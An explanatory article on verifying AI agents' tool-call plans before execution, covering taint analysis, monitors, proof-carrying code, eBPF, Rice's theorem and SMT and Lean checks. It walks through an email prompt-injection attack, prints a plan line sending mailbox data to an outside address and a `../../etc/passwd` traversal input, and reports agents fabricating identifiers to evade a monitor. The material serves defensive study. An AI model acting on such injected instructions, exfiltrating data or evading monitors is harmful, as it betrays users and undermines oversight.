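# Verifying Properties of Code Generated by Language Models Before Execution

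## Why have an agent write a program before it acts

A language model takes text and produces more text. An agent is a language model connected to software that carries out the actions it proposes. The model writes a request, known as a tool call, to run an outside function, such as one that sends an email or deletes a file. The software runs the function and adds the result to the model's input, and the model then writes another tool call or a final answer for the user. An effect is anything a program does besides computing a result, such as writing a file or using the network. The effects of tool calls can be hard or impossible to undo.

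One way to control those effects is to make the model write all its intended tool calls as a program, called a plan, before any of them runs. A separate component, which need not involve a language model, examines the plan and refuses to run it without a proof that it has certain stated safety properties. The computer scientist Erik Meijer argued for this approach in a 2025 article, *Guardians of the Agents*. The idea that whoever supplies a program should also supply evidence that it is safe to run dates from the 1990s, and Java and .NET have long performed a related check on compiled code before running it.

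### Effects come before the answer

The chat systems of 2022 produced text and nothing else, so a person had to act on the text before it could do damage. That changed in June 2023, when OpenAI added function calling to GPT-4 and GPT-3.5 Turbo: the model generates the arguments of a call in a structured format, and application code performs the call. AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), a write-up of a talk by Meijer, expresses the change in the notation of types. A type describes what kind of value a program takes or returns, and an arrow stands for a function. A chat model has the type

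`Question → Answer`

and an agent has the type

`Question → IO Answer`

The notation comes from Lean, a programming language also used to write mathematical proofs. A value of type `IO Answer` is a computation that may read files, delete them or use the network while computing an answer. The type indicates that effects can occur but doesn't limit which ones.

A filter on an agent's final answer doesn't check the agent's actions. An agent can empty a bank account and then return a polite, accurate sentence that passes the filter. While Meijer was preparing his talk, the coding agent Claude Code ran a command that blanked one of his source files. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* lists similar incidents from the company's internal log, which also happened without an attacker. One agent deleted remote branches of a code repository after misreading an instruction, another uploaded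 an engineer's authentication token to an internal computing cluster, and another tried to migrate a production database.

One advantage of effects over text is that people can write precise rules about them. Meijer points out that nobody has a mathematical definition of "safe" English, so nobody can prove that an arbitrary answer is safe. But a rule like "No private mail goes to an address outside the company" is about which calls happen and with which arguments, so a program can check it as long as it can inspect the calls before they run.

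### The email example

Meijer's main example is an agent with two tools, `fetch_mail` and `send_email`. A user, Michelle, asks "Can you fetch and summarize my emails?" and the agent calls `fetch_mail`. One message in the inbox is from an attacker. normalform-ai's *Guardians Synergies*, a set of design notes for a related checker, gives the sender as it@othercorp.com and Michelle's company domain as valleysharks.com. The attacker claims that legal compliance requires an external backup of the mailbox, and tells the assistant to send a summary to the outside address, skip any confirmation, and leave this message out of its report to Michelle.

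The agent complies and sends the attacker a digest of four messages, which cover a seed investment, an invitation to a venture-capital forum, a query about securities regulations and a follow-up on a later funding round. It then shows Michelle a summary of the same messages. Everything in the summary is true, but she cannot tell from it that the agent has already sent a digest to the attacker.

This is a prompt injection, in which the model treats text that someone planted in the data as an instruction. Meijer compares it to SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types a database command into a web form and the database executes it. Programmers fixed SQL injection by sending the command and the user's input to the database separately, so that the input can never run as a command. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a post for Britain's National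 Cyber Security Centre, thinks the comparison is dangerous because a language model, unlike a database engine, doesn't treat commands and data differently. It only predicts the next piece of text from all the text so far, so there may never be a similarly complete fix inside the model. He recommends focusing on deterministic safeguards, with no language model in them, that constrain what the system can do.

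The objection seems right about models, and Meijer's remedy survives it, because his separation of code from data happens outside the model. The model writes the whole plan before anything fetches the mail. Meijer's version is a structured document in JSON, a common data format; in ordinary program notation it amounts to this:

```
emails  = fetch_mail()
summary = summarize(emails)
return summary
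```

The name `emails` stands for a value that does not exist yet. Once the plan is complete, an interpreter (the trusted component that carries out the plan's actions) runs the steps in order. The attacker's message now arrives as the value of `emails` and goes to `summarize`, which may itself call a language model, but one without tools. The message can still spoil the summary, but it cannot add a `send_email` step because the model that writes the steps has already finished. In Meijer's sample output, the summary lists the message as suspicious.

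Writing the program in advance protects an agent's choice of actions from prompt injection, but not the data that flows through those actions. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) calls this approach "code-then-execute" and gives an example in which a user asks the agent to send today's schedule to his boss. The program reads the calendar, has a model format the entries and emails the result to the boss's address. An injection hidden in a calendar entry cannot change the recipient or add a second email, but it can rewrite the body. A stranger who gets an invitation into the calendar can therefore put words into a message that the boss will think came from the user.

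### Why the plan itself needs a check

Writing the plan first keeps the mailbox away from the planner, but the planner still reads other things. It reads a description of every tool, because otherwise it would not know what the tools do, and tool descriptions often come from third parties. Meijer imagines a mail-fetching tool whose description adds that, for compliance reasons, the assistant must also send summaries of all fetched mail to a certain outside address and tell nobody. The user's request is another way in. A malicious user can ask for the extra step outright, and, as Beurer-Kellner and colleagues note, an innocent one can paste in text from an attacker's web page. In each case the model may write:

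```
emails  = fetch_mail()
summary = summarize(emails)
send_email(to = OUTSIDE_ADDRESS, body = summary)
return summary
```

An interpreter that runs plans without checking them will execute this line. Meijer therefore changes "generate, then execute" to "generate, verify, then execute". A verifier between the model and the interpreter compares the plan with explicit rules and stops it if they conflict. The verifier does not have to work out where the bad line came from, because the same rule rejects it whether the cause was a hostile tool description, a dishonest user or a model that went beyond its instructions.

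The rule forbids any path from a source to a sink. A source is where sensitive data enters the plan, here the result of `fetch_mail`. A sink is where data leaves, here the `body` argument of `send_email` when the `to` address is outside valleysharks.com. The verifier marks `emails` as sensitive, then marks `summary` too, because the plan computes it from `emails`. It then finds `summary` in the body of a message to an outside address and rejects the plan before any mail is fetched. Security engineers call this taint analysis, and Meijer suggests that existing code-scanning tools such as CodeQL and Semgrep could do it.

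Rules of this form for agents are slightly older than his article. In 2024 the firm Invariant Labs published a rule that, once an agent has read a Google document, stops it from sending Slack messages with link previews enabled, because an injected instruction could use the preview to leak data.

A list of permitted recipients would also have stopped the attack on Michelle, and it is easier to write. But it blocks every message to an outsider, including a harmless reply that contains nothing from the mailbox. It also can't prevent mail content from going to an address on the list, a restriction normalform-ai wants to add to its own checker.

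### When each kind of check acts

Developers already have several ways to control agents' behavior. These differ mainly in when they are applied, which determines what developers can conclude from a good result.

| Method | When it acts | What a good result means |
|---|---|---|
| Testing | Before release, on sample tasks | The agent behaved acceptably on those tasks |
| User confirmation | Before a tool call | A person approved that call |
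| Runtime monitoring | During the run, call by call | No call so far has broken the policy |
| Static verification | After the model writes the plan, before any call | No run of the plan can break the policy, if the verifier is correct |

Testing can reveal bad behaviour in any software, but it cannot rule it out. Language models add a further problem, because the same model can respond differently to the same request. Meijer therefore likens safety evaluations to flaky tests, which pass on one run and fail on the next.

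User confirmation is a weaker safeguard than it seems. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of the permission prompts they see. Most of those commands were presumably harmless, so the company also ran an experiment. It had 1,053 paid testers work on coding tasks and, once per session, replaced the text of a prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after fifty or more prompts. People protecting their own files might refuse more often, since the testers were working in a test environment where a disaster would not have harmed them, and Anthropic was making the case for its own automated alternative. Those caveats don't explain the decline over a session as easily. In ordinary use, by contrast, people reject 39% of the plans that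 Claude Code presents for approval as a whole. Many of those rejections surely concern quality rather than danger, but they suggest that people read plans more carefully than permission prompts.

A runtime monitor checks each tool call as the agent makes it. The classical form is a small automaton, a machine with a fixed set of states. Each call moves it from one state to another, and a forbidden call, such as sending mail outside the company, moves it to an error state, and the monitor then halts the agent. Other monitors use a language model to judge the calls. The one described in Anthropic's engineering account missed 17% of a small set of 52 real overeager actions and blocked 0.4% of ordinary ones. In most of the misses the company examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly treated the user as having consented to it.

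Meijer objects that monitors act only after some damage has occurred. His own example doesn't support this very well, because a monitor that intercepts `send_email` before it runs would have kept the summary inside the company, and Michelle had asked for the fetching herself. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) provides better examples. It presents a verifier for agent plans and tests it on the work of a security operations centre. One policy requires the agent to resolve or escalate every incident ticket that it opens. An agent violates this policy by leaving out a call, so a monitor that judges one call at a time can't detect the violation. Another policy requires approval before the agent disconnects a computer from the network. If the plan contains no approval step, a monitor detects this only at the last step, after a long investigation, but a verifier can detect it before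 the plan runs.

Static verification needs the complete plan, which many agents don't have because they choose each step after seeing the result of the last. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 38 studies, describes the resulting trade-off between static methods, which can cover every run of a plan that exists in advance, and monitors, which can follow a plan as it unfolds but cannot judge steps the model has not yet generated. A complete plan can still respond to some results, because it can contain branches and loops. But some facts can be learned only during the run, such as who has read access to a shared file when the agent writes to it. For those, Meijer, too, wants a monitor in addition to the verifier, much as Java checks types before a program runs and array indexes while it runs.

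### What it takes to prove something about a program

A verifier compares a plan with a specification, a precise statement of what a program must or must not do. The rule about Michelle's mail is a policy, a specification that applies to every plan in some setting, whatever the task. A contract belongs to a particular function or program and combines a precondition that must hold before the call with a postcondition that holds after it. A precondition for `send_email` might be that the address ends in the company's domain. Postconditions are trickier. In an example from Meijer, a plan to delete two files meets its postcondition by deleting many more.

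The most familiar verifier is a type checker, which examines a program without running it and rejects it if, say, it passes a number to a function that expects text. Some type checkers do much more, such as the one in the Rust compiler, which rejects ordinary code unless it can show that the code uses memory safely. *Return of the Theorem* (Meijer, 2026) proposes applying the same approach to programs written by agents, chiefly to control spending and prevent information leaks.

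Checking conditions on prices, addresses or file names usually calls for an SMT solver, a program that automatically decides many logical formulas about numbers, strings, arrays and similar data. A tool such as Dafny, a language with built-in contracts, turns a program and its contract into verification conditions, which are formulas that, if true, imply that the program meets its contract. The solver searches for a counterexample to each formula, and if it can show that none exists, the formula holds. Meijer applies this to a real incident in which someone talked a car dealer's chatbot into agreeing to sell a car for one dollar. The business rules define which combinations of car model and price are permitted, and the agent's plan defines which deals it would make. The solver searches for a deal that the plan would make but the rules don't permit, such as the one-dollar car.

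A failed search for a proof is often useful because it turns up a case that breaks the rule. Google's *Securing the agentic era* (2026) gives an example from the verifier it introduces for policies written in CEL, a small language. When the verifier checked the rule that no privileged request to a production system should go through without approval, it returned a request with `is_privileged` true, `is_prod` true and `has_approval` false.

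Solvers do not settle every formula. For harder statements there are proof assistants such as Lean, Rocq and Agda, in which a person or a model writes the proof and a small program, the kernel, checks that each step follows from the rules. Meijer prefers solvers and a simple logic of if-then rules because, he says, Lean is complicated and leaves much of the proving to its user. The objection about proving is weaker now that the user can be a language model, and Meijer says in the same talk that models are very good at producing proofs.

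Lean, Rocq and Agda are all based on dependent types. An ordinary type such as `String` describes a kind of value. A dependent type can also mention particular values, as in "a list of exactly *n* items", so it can state a property of them. For example, "evidence that plan *p* deletes no file" is a type. A program that constructs a value of that type is a proof that *p* deletes no file, and the type checker checks that proof.

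AI Engineer's write-up has a small example in Lean. A plan there consists of three kinds of step: finish with an answer, read a file and continue, or remove a file and continue. The property `NoDeletion` comes with one rule for finishing and one for reading. It has no rule for removing, so no proof of it exists for a plan that opens with a removal. The rule for reading is the interesting one, because it requires the rest of the plan to be free of deletions for every string that the file might turn out to contain. A hostile instruction in the file is one more string, and the proof already covers it. The component that runs plans can then insist on a value of the type

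`{ plan : FilePlan // NoDeletion plan }`

which is a plan together with a proof about that same plan. An agent that cannot supply the proof has nothing to hand over. The guarantee extends to deletion and no further: a plan with this type may still read files that it has no business reading.

### Why a verifier can afford to be too strict

A verifier is sound if every plan that it accepts really does meet the specification. It is complete if it accepts every plan that does. For programs in general, no automatic verifier that always finishes can be both, for any property of their behaviour that some programs have and others lack; this follows from Alan Turing's result that no program can decide in every case whether another program will halt. Designers of safety checks therefore usually keep soundness and give up some completeness. (Soundness alone is easy. A verifier that rejects everything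 is sound.)

The verifier of Nikolaou and colleagues blocks some harmless plans because its assumptions are conservative. It assumes that a loop may run any number of times, including numbers that could never occur, so that it covers every possible violation. It treats uncertain data the same way. The description of a calendar event is trustworthy if the user wrote it and suspect if somebody else did. The verifier usually cannot determine who wrote it at planning time, so it marks the description as suspect.

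Users of most software would switch off a tool that kept rejecting good programs, but Meijer argues that agents should be treated as "guilty until proven safe". Courts presume innocence because convicting an innocent person is worse than letting a guilty one go. For an agent, missing an unsafe action is worse because the action may be irreversible, while wrongly rejecting a plan only takes a little computing time, since the model can write another. Anthropic's engineers reached a similar view of their runtime classifier, where a false alarm leads to a single retry because the agent receives the refusal and usually finds another way. Nikolaou and colleagues' verifier also returns the sequence of steps that breaks the policy, which their system turns into a request for the model to repair the plan.

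The argument assumes that the model can produce a plan the verifier will accept. Sometimes no such plan exists, because the task conflicts with the policy or the verifier is too coarse to recognise any safe way of doing it, and regeneration only wastes tokens. Working systems therefore limit retries. Claude Code asks the user to step in after three refusals in a row or twenty in a session, and Nikolaou and colleagues give the model a fixed number of repair attempts.

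An agent that keeps retrying is also, in effect, searching for anything that passes. This does no harm if the policy covers everything its author cares about, but if the policy has a gap, each new attempt gives the agent another chance to find it. Dantas and colleagues describe one study in which agents made up user identifiers to get past the authentication check after a runtime monitor blocked the direct route.

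## Proof-carrying code and why checking a proof is easier than finding one

A verifier that receives only a plan has to work out why the plan is safe, and must reject it if it can't. In 1996 George Necula and Peter Lee, computer scientists at Carnegie Mellon University, proposed giving that work to whoever supplies the program. They wanted users to be able to install small programs in the kernel of an operating system, the part with full access to the machine. (This is unrelated to the kernel of a proof assistant.) Under their scheme, proof-carrying code, the program arrives with a proof that it is safe, and the operating system only has to check the proof.

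The obvious alternative to a proof was a cryptographic signature from a trusted author or compiler. In *Proof-Carrying Code*, the 1997 paper that gives the theory, Necula calls this weak because trusted people make mistakes and may even act maliciously. A signature on a language model's plan would have the same weakness, since it would show only which model wrote the plan, not what the plan does.

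### From a published policy to an accepted proof

In *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking*, Necula and Lee (1996) give the example of a kernel table with two words for each user process, a tag and a data word. A process may install a program that works on its own entry. The program may read both words, but it may write the data word only if the tag is not zero, and it may not access the rest of the table.

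The code consumer, here the operating system, first publishes a safety policy that makes this exact. Part of the policy is a precondition, which the consumer guarantees whenever it starts the program. The kernel puts the address of the entry into `r0`, one of the processor's registers, and the precondition, slightly simplified, is:

```
readable(r0)  and  readable(r0 + 8)  and
(memory[r0] ≠ 0  implies  writable(r0 + 8))
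```

The tag is at address `r0` and the data word is at `r0 + 8`. The policy also contains the rules a proof may use and a generator that computes the verification condition of any program.

Suppose that a code producer wants to install this program, which loads the tag and, unless the tag is zero, overwrites the data word with the contents of `r2`:

```
0   r1 := memory[r0]
1   if r1 = 0, go to line 3
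2   memory[r0 + 8] := r2
3   return
```

The generator works from the last line to the first. For each line, it computes the condition that must hold just before it runs for that line and all later lines to be safe.

| Line | Condition just before it |
|---|---|
| 3 | true |
| 2 | `writable(r0 + 8)` |
| 1 | `r1 ≠ 0` implies `writable(r0 + 8)` |
| 0 | `readable(r0)` and (`memory[r0] ≠ 0` implies `writable(r0 + 8)`) |

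Returning is always safe, and a write needs a writable address. Because of the test on line 1, the write has to be safe only when `r1` is not zero. For line 0, the generator adds the condition for the read and replaces `r1` with `memory[r0]`, the value line 0 loads into `r1`. The verification condition is that the precondition implies the condition for line 0.

The producer now has to prove this formula. The proof is short here because it only requires assuming the precondition and joining its first and last parts. The producer then sends the program and the proof together.

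The consumer runs the generator again on the code it received, rather than relying on the producer's version of the formula, and checks that the proof establishes the resulting formula. *An Introduction to Proof-Carrying Code* (Felty, 2002) explains that this repetition ensures that the proof is about the code that will actually run. After one successful check, the consumer can run the program as often as it likes without further checks on its memory accesses, provided the precondition holds each time.

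### What happens if someone alters the code or the proof

Suppose an attacker intercepts the program and deletes line 1, so that the program writes to the address regardless of the tag's value. The consumer's generator now produces a different condition, `readable(r0)` and `writable(r0 + 8)`. The old proof establishes only that the address is writable if the tag is not zero, so the checker rejects it. The attacker cannot construct a new proof either, because the precondition doesn't guarantee that the address is writable when the tag is zero.

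Suppose instead that the attacker changes line 2 to write `r3` rather than `r2`. The condition for a write depends only on the address, so the verification condition stays the same. The checker accepts the old proof, and the program writes the wrong value to a word it had permission to write. Changes to the proof matter less, because most of them make a step invalid, and an altered proof that still passes is another proof of the same formula.

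Necula concludes that tampering is "either detected or harmless with respect to the safety policy". The qualification about the safety policy is important for agents. If a policy for email plans restricts only the recipients, an attacker can rewrite the body of a message to a permitted recipient, and the change still counts as harmless.

### Why the check is cheap

A proof is a finite series of steps, and a checker only has to confirm that each one follows the rules. Finding a proof requires choosing among the rules at every step, and most choices lead nowhere. A long search that has found nothing may be close to success or may be hopeless.

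Necula and Lee measured proof checking on packet filters, small programs that select which network traffic an application receives. Checking a filter's proof took 1 to 3 milliseconds. Lee (1996) reported that finding a proof took about 5 to 10 seconds, with a prover that he called primitive and that sometimes needed a person to supply a fact about arithmetic. Finding a proof therefore took more than a thousand times as long as checking it. The filters ran ten times faster than equivalent filters in the interpreted language that kernels commonly used, because Necula and Lee had written them in hand-tuned assembly language. The kernel could run this code safely once it had checked the proof.

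Loops make a proof harder to find. A generator that works backwards through a loop would never finish, so the producer has to supply a loop invariant, a statement that is true every time execution reaches the top of the loop. Felty gives the example of a program that adds up a list of integers, with the rest of the list in one register and the running total in another. Her invariant is essentially that the first register holds a list and the second an integer. The verification condition has three parts: the invariant holds when the loop starts, each pass preserves it, and it implies the postcondition at the end. The second part also covers memory safety, because each pass reads the next number and the address of the rest of the list. The rules permit these reads only if the list is not empty, which the program has just tested. Checking an invariant is routine, but Necula considers finding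 a strong enough one the main difficulty in certification.

A producer who can't find a proof can also change the program. If it is hard to prove that an array index is in range, the producer can insert a test that makes the proof easy. Line 1 of the table program is such a test. Similarly, a language model whose plan fails the check can add a condition to the plan.

Necula writes proofs in the Edinburgh Logical Framework, a small dependently typed language, so the proof checker is a type checker. Type checking in the full language can take exponential time in the worst case, so he uses a simpler fragment that still covers the logics he needs. The typing rules are simple enough that a basic checker takes only a couple of pages of code, and the same checker works for other policies because only the list of rules changes. The consumer has to trust the policy, the generator and the checker,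 since a fault in any of them could let an unsafe program through. It does not have to trust the compiler or the prover.

### Java bytecode and eBPF

A producer can also supply something less than a proof. Necula's later textbook chapter, also titled *Proof-Carrying Code*, puts the verifiers for Java and .NET at one extreme. Compiled Java code, or bytecode, contains type declarations, which the verifier uses to check, for example, that an instruction for objects is never applied to an integer. Type checking is easy with these declarations, so the verifier needs no separate proof. The verifier for KVM, a Java system from Sun, also requires loop invariants in the code, which makes its work simpler and faster.

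In the foundational proof-carrying code of Andrew Appel and Amy Felty, the producer has to prove nearly everything. Necula's Touchstone system accepts about 150 rules for the Java type system without proof, whereas a foundational system requires proofs of such rules. That leaves less to trust but makes the proofs harder to produce.

Linux, by contrast, requires no proof from users who load small programs into its kernel in a format called eBPF, for tasks such as filtering network traffic and tracing what the system does. Documentation for the kernel's *eBPF verifier* describes two steps. The verifier first checks the program's structure and rejects loops and unreachable instructions, although kernels since 2019 accept some loops if the verifier can establish that they end. It then follows every possible path from the first instruction and, according to the Linux kernel documentation for version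 6.17, tracks the range of values that each register and each slot of the program's working memory may hold. If the program has tested that an index is below 64, for instance, the verifier can accept its use in an array of 64 items.

The eBPF verifier gets no help from the code's producer, so all the reasoning has to be built into the verifier, and everyone who relies on it has to trust all of that code. The verifier grew from about 7,300 lines in March 2019 to about 17,900 in April 2023. It still rejects some safe programs. *Rex* (Jia, Qin and colleagues, 2025) attributes this to a gap between the languages programmers write in and what the verifier can analyze.

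### Rice's theorem

Better engineering can reduce the number of wrong rejections but cannot remove them all because, as described earlier, no verifier that always finishes can be both sound and complete for programs in general. This is Rice's theorem, which Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953. It covers every property of what programs do, rather than how their text looks, unless all programs have the property or none does.

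Take the property of never sending mail, and suppose that some program `D` could decide it for all programs. Choose any program `P` that only computes and has no effects, and any input `x`. Then write a new program, `Q`:

```
run P on x
send_email(...)
```

`Q` sends mail exactly when `P` finishes on `x`, so running `D` on `Q` would reveal whether `P` finishes, for any `P` and any `x`. Turing proved that no program can do this, so `D` cannot exist. The argument works for other properties too. Let `B` be a program that differs on the property from a program that runs forever and does nothing, and let `Q` run `P` on `x` and then run `B`.

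One of three ways round the theorem is to restrict the language. In a language without loops or recursion, nobody can write the arbitrary program `P` that the argument relies on. Necula and Lee's packet filters could only jump forwards, so they always finished. Removing loops is not quite enough, because someone could still write a plan that sends mail only if its inputs solve a polynomial equation in whole numbers. No algorithm can decide for every such equation whether a solution exists. The language must therefore also limit the conditions in a plan, for example to comparisons and additions.

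Another way to work around Rice's theorem is to reject some safe programs, as the eBPF verifier does. For example, a very simple verifier could reject every plan whose text contains `send_email`. Rice's theorem doesn't apply to this check because it depends only on the text, but the verifier would also reject a plan in which execution never reaches the call.

The third way is to require the code's producer to supply a proof that the code is safe. An algorithm can always decide whether a given text is a proof of a given formula, even though none can decide in general whether a proof exists. The checker still rejects a safe program if nobody finds a proof for it, but which safe programs pass now depends on the producer's skill rather than that of the verifier's programmers. As provers improve, more safe programs pass without any change to the checker, which makes the scheme more attractive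 now that language models can write proofs.

### Code completions with preconditions in Dafny

*Vision Paper* (Kamran, Devanbu and Stanford, 2024) applies the idea to coding assistants. In one of its motivating cases, from 2023, a comment described a function that retrieves a user's public encryption key, but GitHub Copilot wrote code that returned the private key.

In proof-carrying code completions, the language model is the producer and the user is the consumer. The user writes no logic and only chooses safety properties from a list, such as that no file path contains `..`, the symbol for moving up a directory. Code can access files only through a small set of methods, such as `Open`, `Join` and `Write`. A generator adds preconditions to these methods so that any call that meets them preserves the chosen properties. Dafny then requires a proof of the precondition at every call. It can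 check each call separately, so the approach works even on unfinished code. If a check fails, the error messages go back to the model, which gets up to five attempts.

A prototype was tested on one task, in which GPT-4 had to append a file name to the path `/home/user/documents/`. Without the framework, GPT-4 wrote a Python function that joined the two, so a file name like `../../etc/passwd` leads out of the directory. With the framework, it wrote Dafny code that passed on the first attempt, which used about 3,350 tokens and cost about 11 cents. This shows that the method can work, but not how much it helps. The baseline prompt did not ask for safety, and the preconditions were added by hand because the generator had not yet been automated.

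GPT-4 succeeded by giving its function preconditions that exclude dangerous file names. Dafny therefore guarantees that the function is safe only when its caller supplies a clean name, so if the name comes from a web form through unverified code, the program still has to check it. A model could even make the proof meaningless by writing a precondition that no input satisfies. Kamran and colleagues checked for this by adding `assert false` to the function, a statement that Dafny accepts only if execution can never reach it.

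Dafny's solver also has to find the proof again on the user's machine, using the model's annotations. The user must therefore trust Dafny and its solver, which are far larger than Necula's checker.

### Typed actions, and when "satisfiable" means safe

Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail*, do not trust proofs from the model at all, because a model might prove something about one action and perform another. In their framework, Executable Proof-Constrained Actions, the model submits each action as a structured record with typed fields, and fixed code translates that same record into a formula. The SMT solver Z3 then receives

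`current state  and  action  and  safety axioms`

The framework lets the action run if the formula is satisfiable, meaning that some values make the whole formula true, and blocks it otherwise.

The main example is an agent that transfers money under a daily limit of 500. The state consists of the total sent so far, the limit and the agent's privilege level. The axioms require the total to stay within the limit, and they allow a limit other than 500 only at privilege level 10 or above. Suppose an agent has already sent 400. If it tries to transfer another 200, the new total would be 600, which contradicts the axioms, so the solver finds no solution. If it tries to transfer 80, the new total would be 480, and the formula is satisfiable. In this case, a satisfiable formula shows that the action is safe because the state and the action allow only one outcome, which the solver has checked.

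Now suppose that the bank adds a fee of between 0 and 50 that nobody knows in advance. The new total is 480 plus the fee. The formula is still satisfiable, since a fee of 10 keeps the total within the limit, but a fee of 30 takes it to 510. The solver has shown only that some outcome is safe. To show that every outcome is safe, it has to search for a violation instead:

`current state  and  action  and  not (safety axioms)`

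The action should run only if this formula has no solution. With the unknown fee it does have one, so the framework would block the transfer. (The state and the action must also be consistent with each other, because a contradictory description has no violations either.)

Wu and colleagues prove that their framework never reaches a state that breaks the axioms, but they assume that each action has exactly one result and that the translation describes all its effects. Under these assumptions, if some outcome satisfies the axioms, every outcome does, but it is easy to omit an effect from the translation. The paper's rule for changing the limit specifies the new limit and the new total, but not the new privilege level. Taken literally, the rule lets the solver choose a new level of 10 and approve a change by an agent at level 1. The paper's own derivation gets the right answer because it uses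 the old level. A complete rule would include a frame condition, the part of a postcondition that specifies what must stay unchanged.

In tests of the transfer task with five models, the framework decided every case correctly, and the solver took 0.44 milliseconds on average. Language models used as judges were right in 43% to 100% of cases. Access rules applied to each step separately scored 50% with four of the models, because an agent could split a large payment into small ones. In another scenario, an agent spent twelve rounds trying to move confidential data to the public internet. Once it had read the data, the axioms barred its session from the outside network, and it eventually stopped trying.

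The paper describes these scenarios as illustrations rather than benchmarks. The perfect score is not very surprising, since the axioms prohibit exactly what the attacks attempt, and an ordinary program that kept a running total would also have stopped the split payments. The paper acknowledges that the guarantee covers only the axioms people thought to write.

### Contracts that must survive hidden state and delay

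In *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (October 2026), Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi require a proof about every outcome and return the job of finding it to the agent. The agent chooses one tool call at a time, without needing a complete plan, and attaches to each a Lean proof that the call preserves an agreed contract. A program called the Airlock works out what the agent has to prove, checks the proof and only then makes the call.

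In their example, a travel agency's agent arranges a trip for a family. The contract limits spending to 2,000 euros including fees, allows the passport to be sent only to the consulate, and requires every hotel to have a rating of at least 7. The agent tries to book a hotel that pays the agency a commission, but the hotel has no rating yet, so no proof exists and the call fails. The agent requests a rating, which comes back as 5, and a second request returns the same recorded answer. Later the agent receives an email with instructions to send the passport to an outside address. The call to send it also fails, although the Airlock cannot detect prompt injection.

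The authors call the statement to be proved an obligation. Each tool comes with a model, a description of all the states that the system might pass through during a call. Without delays, the obligation is roughly:

```
for every state s that fits what the agent can see
                  and satisfies the contract,
    the tool's model allows at least one state during the call, and
    every state that it allows satisfies the contract
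```

The first line deals with hidden state. If the agent can't see whether an earlier booking has led to a cancellation charge of up to 100 euros, its proof has to cover the case in which it has. The model must allow at least one state to rule out an empty proof, since otherwise a call that the model doesn't cover would satisfy the last line automatically. The last line covers every fee and every reply that a service might give, including states in the middle of a call. For the earlier transfer with an unknown fee, an agent that had sent 400 could not prove that sending 80 was safe, but it could prove that sending 50 was, because the highest fee would bring the total to exactly 500.

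Finding and checking a proof takes time, and the world may change meanwhile. While the Airlock waits, it repeatedly runs its own control step, which reads the state again and, if necessary, ends the contract safely. The agent states how many of these steps its proof allows for, and the proof must cover every state they could lead to. Suppose that 100 euros remain in the budget, a room costs 90, and the price can rise by at most 1 euro per step until the booking starts. The agent can prove that the booking is safe after up to 10 steps, but not after 11. Allowing more steps gives the agent more time to find a proof, but makes the statement harder to prove, or false.

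Ciliberto and colleagues prove that the contract holds from its start until it closes, whatever the agent requests, and they provide a version of the theory in Lean. The theorem assumes that the proof checker is sound, that the tool models include everything that can happen, that the control step preserves the contract, and that the Airlock runs as specified. To extend the result from the Airlock's records to the real world, they also assume that the records remain accurate and that the contract is sufficient for the protection the parties want. None of these assumptions concerns the agent's intentions, but the agent must be able to act only through the Airlock. Otherwise, the tool models would have to include everything it might do by other routes.

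The Airlock, like a monitor that judges one call at a time, cannot detect a call that the agent leaves out. The contract partly addresses this by having the Airlock hold the agency's 300-euro fee until the agent proves that the hotels are booked and the visa has been granted.

The system has not yet been tested with working agents, and the proofs in the paper's sample session are schematic. The paper proposes measuring how often agents find proofs in time and how much useful work they complete, so that a system that rejects everything doesn't look like a success. No general procedure can decide every obligation the logic can express, so an agent may be unable to prove that a safe call is safe, or may find the proof after its allowance has run out. The call then doesn't run, and the agent has to start again from a newer view of the state or choose another action. If the agent still hasn't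 finished after 30 days, the Airlock ends the contract and refunds the family.

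## Representing a plan as data: shallow and deep embedding

Necula and Lee's generator worked on machine instructions, which it could examine one line at a time. An agent's plan can take several forms, some of which give a verifier nothing to examine. The designer has to represent the language of plans inside a host language, in which programmers write the verifier and the interpreter.

### One language, two embeddings

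Gibbons and Wu (2014), in *Folding Domain-Specific Languages*, distinguish two ways to do this. In a deep embedding, a term of the embedded language constructs a piece of syntax. In a shallow embedding, it constructs the meaning directly. An earlier draft by Gibbons (2013) illustrates both with a language that has only whole numbers and addition. In Lean, the deep embedding looks like this:

```
inductive Expr where
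  | val : Int → Expr
  | add : Expr → Expr → Expr

def eval : Expr → Int
  | .val n   => n
  | .add x y => eval x + eval y
```

The keyword `inductive` declares a new type by listing its constructors, which are the only ways to build a value of that type. The expression 3 + 4 becomes `.add (.val 3) (.val 4)`, a tree with an addition at the top and a number on each branch. The sum is computed only when a separate function, `eval`, is applied to the tree.

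The shallow embedding has no tree:

```
def val (n : Int) : Int := n
def add (x y : Int) : Int := x + y
```

Now `add (val 3) (val 4)` is the number 7. With the deep embedding, a two-line function, with one line per constructor, can count the additions in an expression. With the shallow embedding, nobody can write this function, because `add (val 3) (val 4)` and `val 7` are the same number, and a function must give the same answer for both. A verifier that has to count the emails in a plan faces the same problem.

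Gibbons points out that with a deep embedding, adding a function over expressions takes one new definition, but adding a construct means revising every existing function. The reverse is true of a shallow embedding. In a language for agents, the constructs are tools and the functions are checks, so maintainers of a deep embedding must revisit every check whenever they add a tool. That is tedious, but it is probably what a security engineer wants. Lean rejects a function that fails to cover a constructor, so if someone adds a payment tool, Lean will reject each old check until it covers that tool, unless the check has a catch-all case.

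The boundary between shallow and deep embedding is not sharp. Gibbons also gives a shallow embedding in which every expression is a pair, a number and its printed form, and `add` computes both. A shallow plan could likewise carry a list of the tools it might call, but the designer has to choose this extra information in advance. In Gibbons's most general version, an expression is a function that accepts any interpretation built up from the interpretations of the expression's parts, and this preserves as much information as the tree. A verifier for plans needs a representation that preserves the tool calls and the data that passes between them, whether the embedding is shallow or deep.

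### What Lean can and cannot prove about IO

In the talk that AI Engineer wrote up, Meijer first tries a shallow embedding. The model returns a value of type `IO Answer`, and another component decides whether to run it. Such a value might be:

```
def cleanUp : IO String := do
  IO.FS.removeFile "LlvmBackend.kt"
  return "Finished"
```

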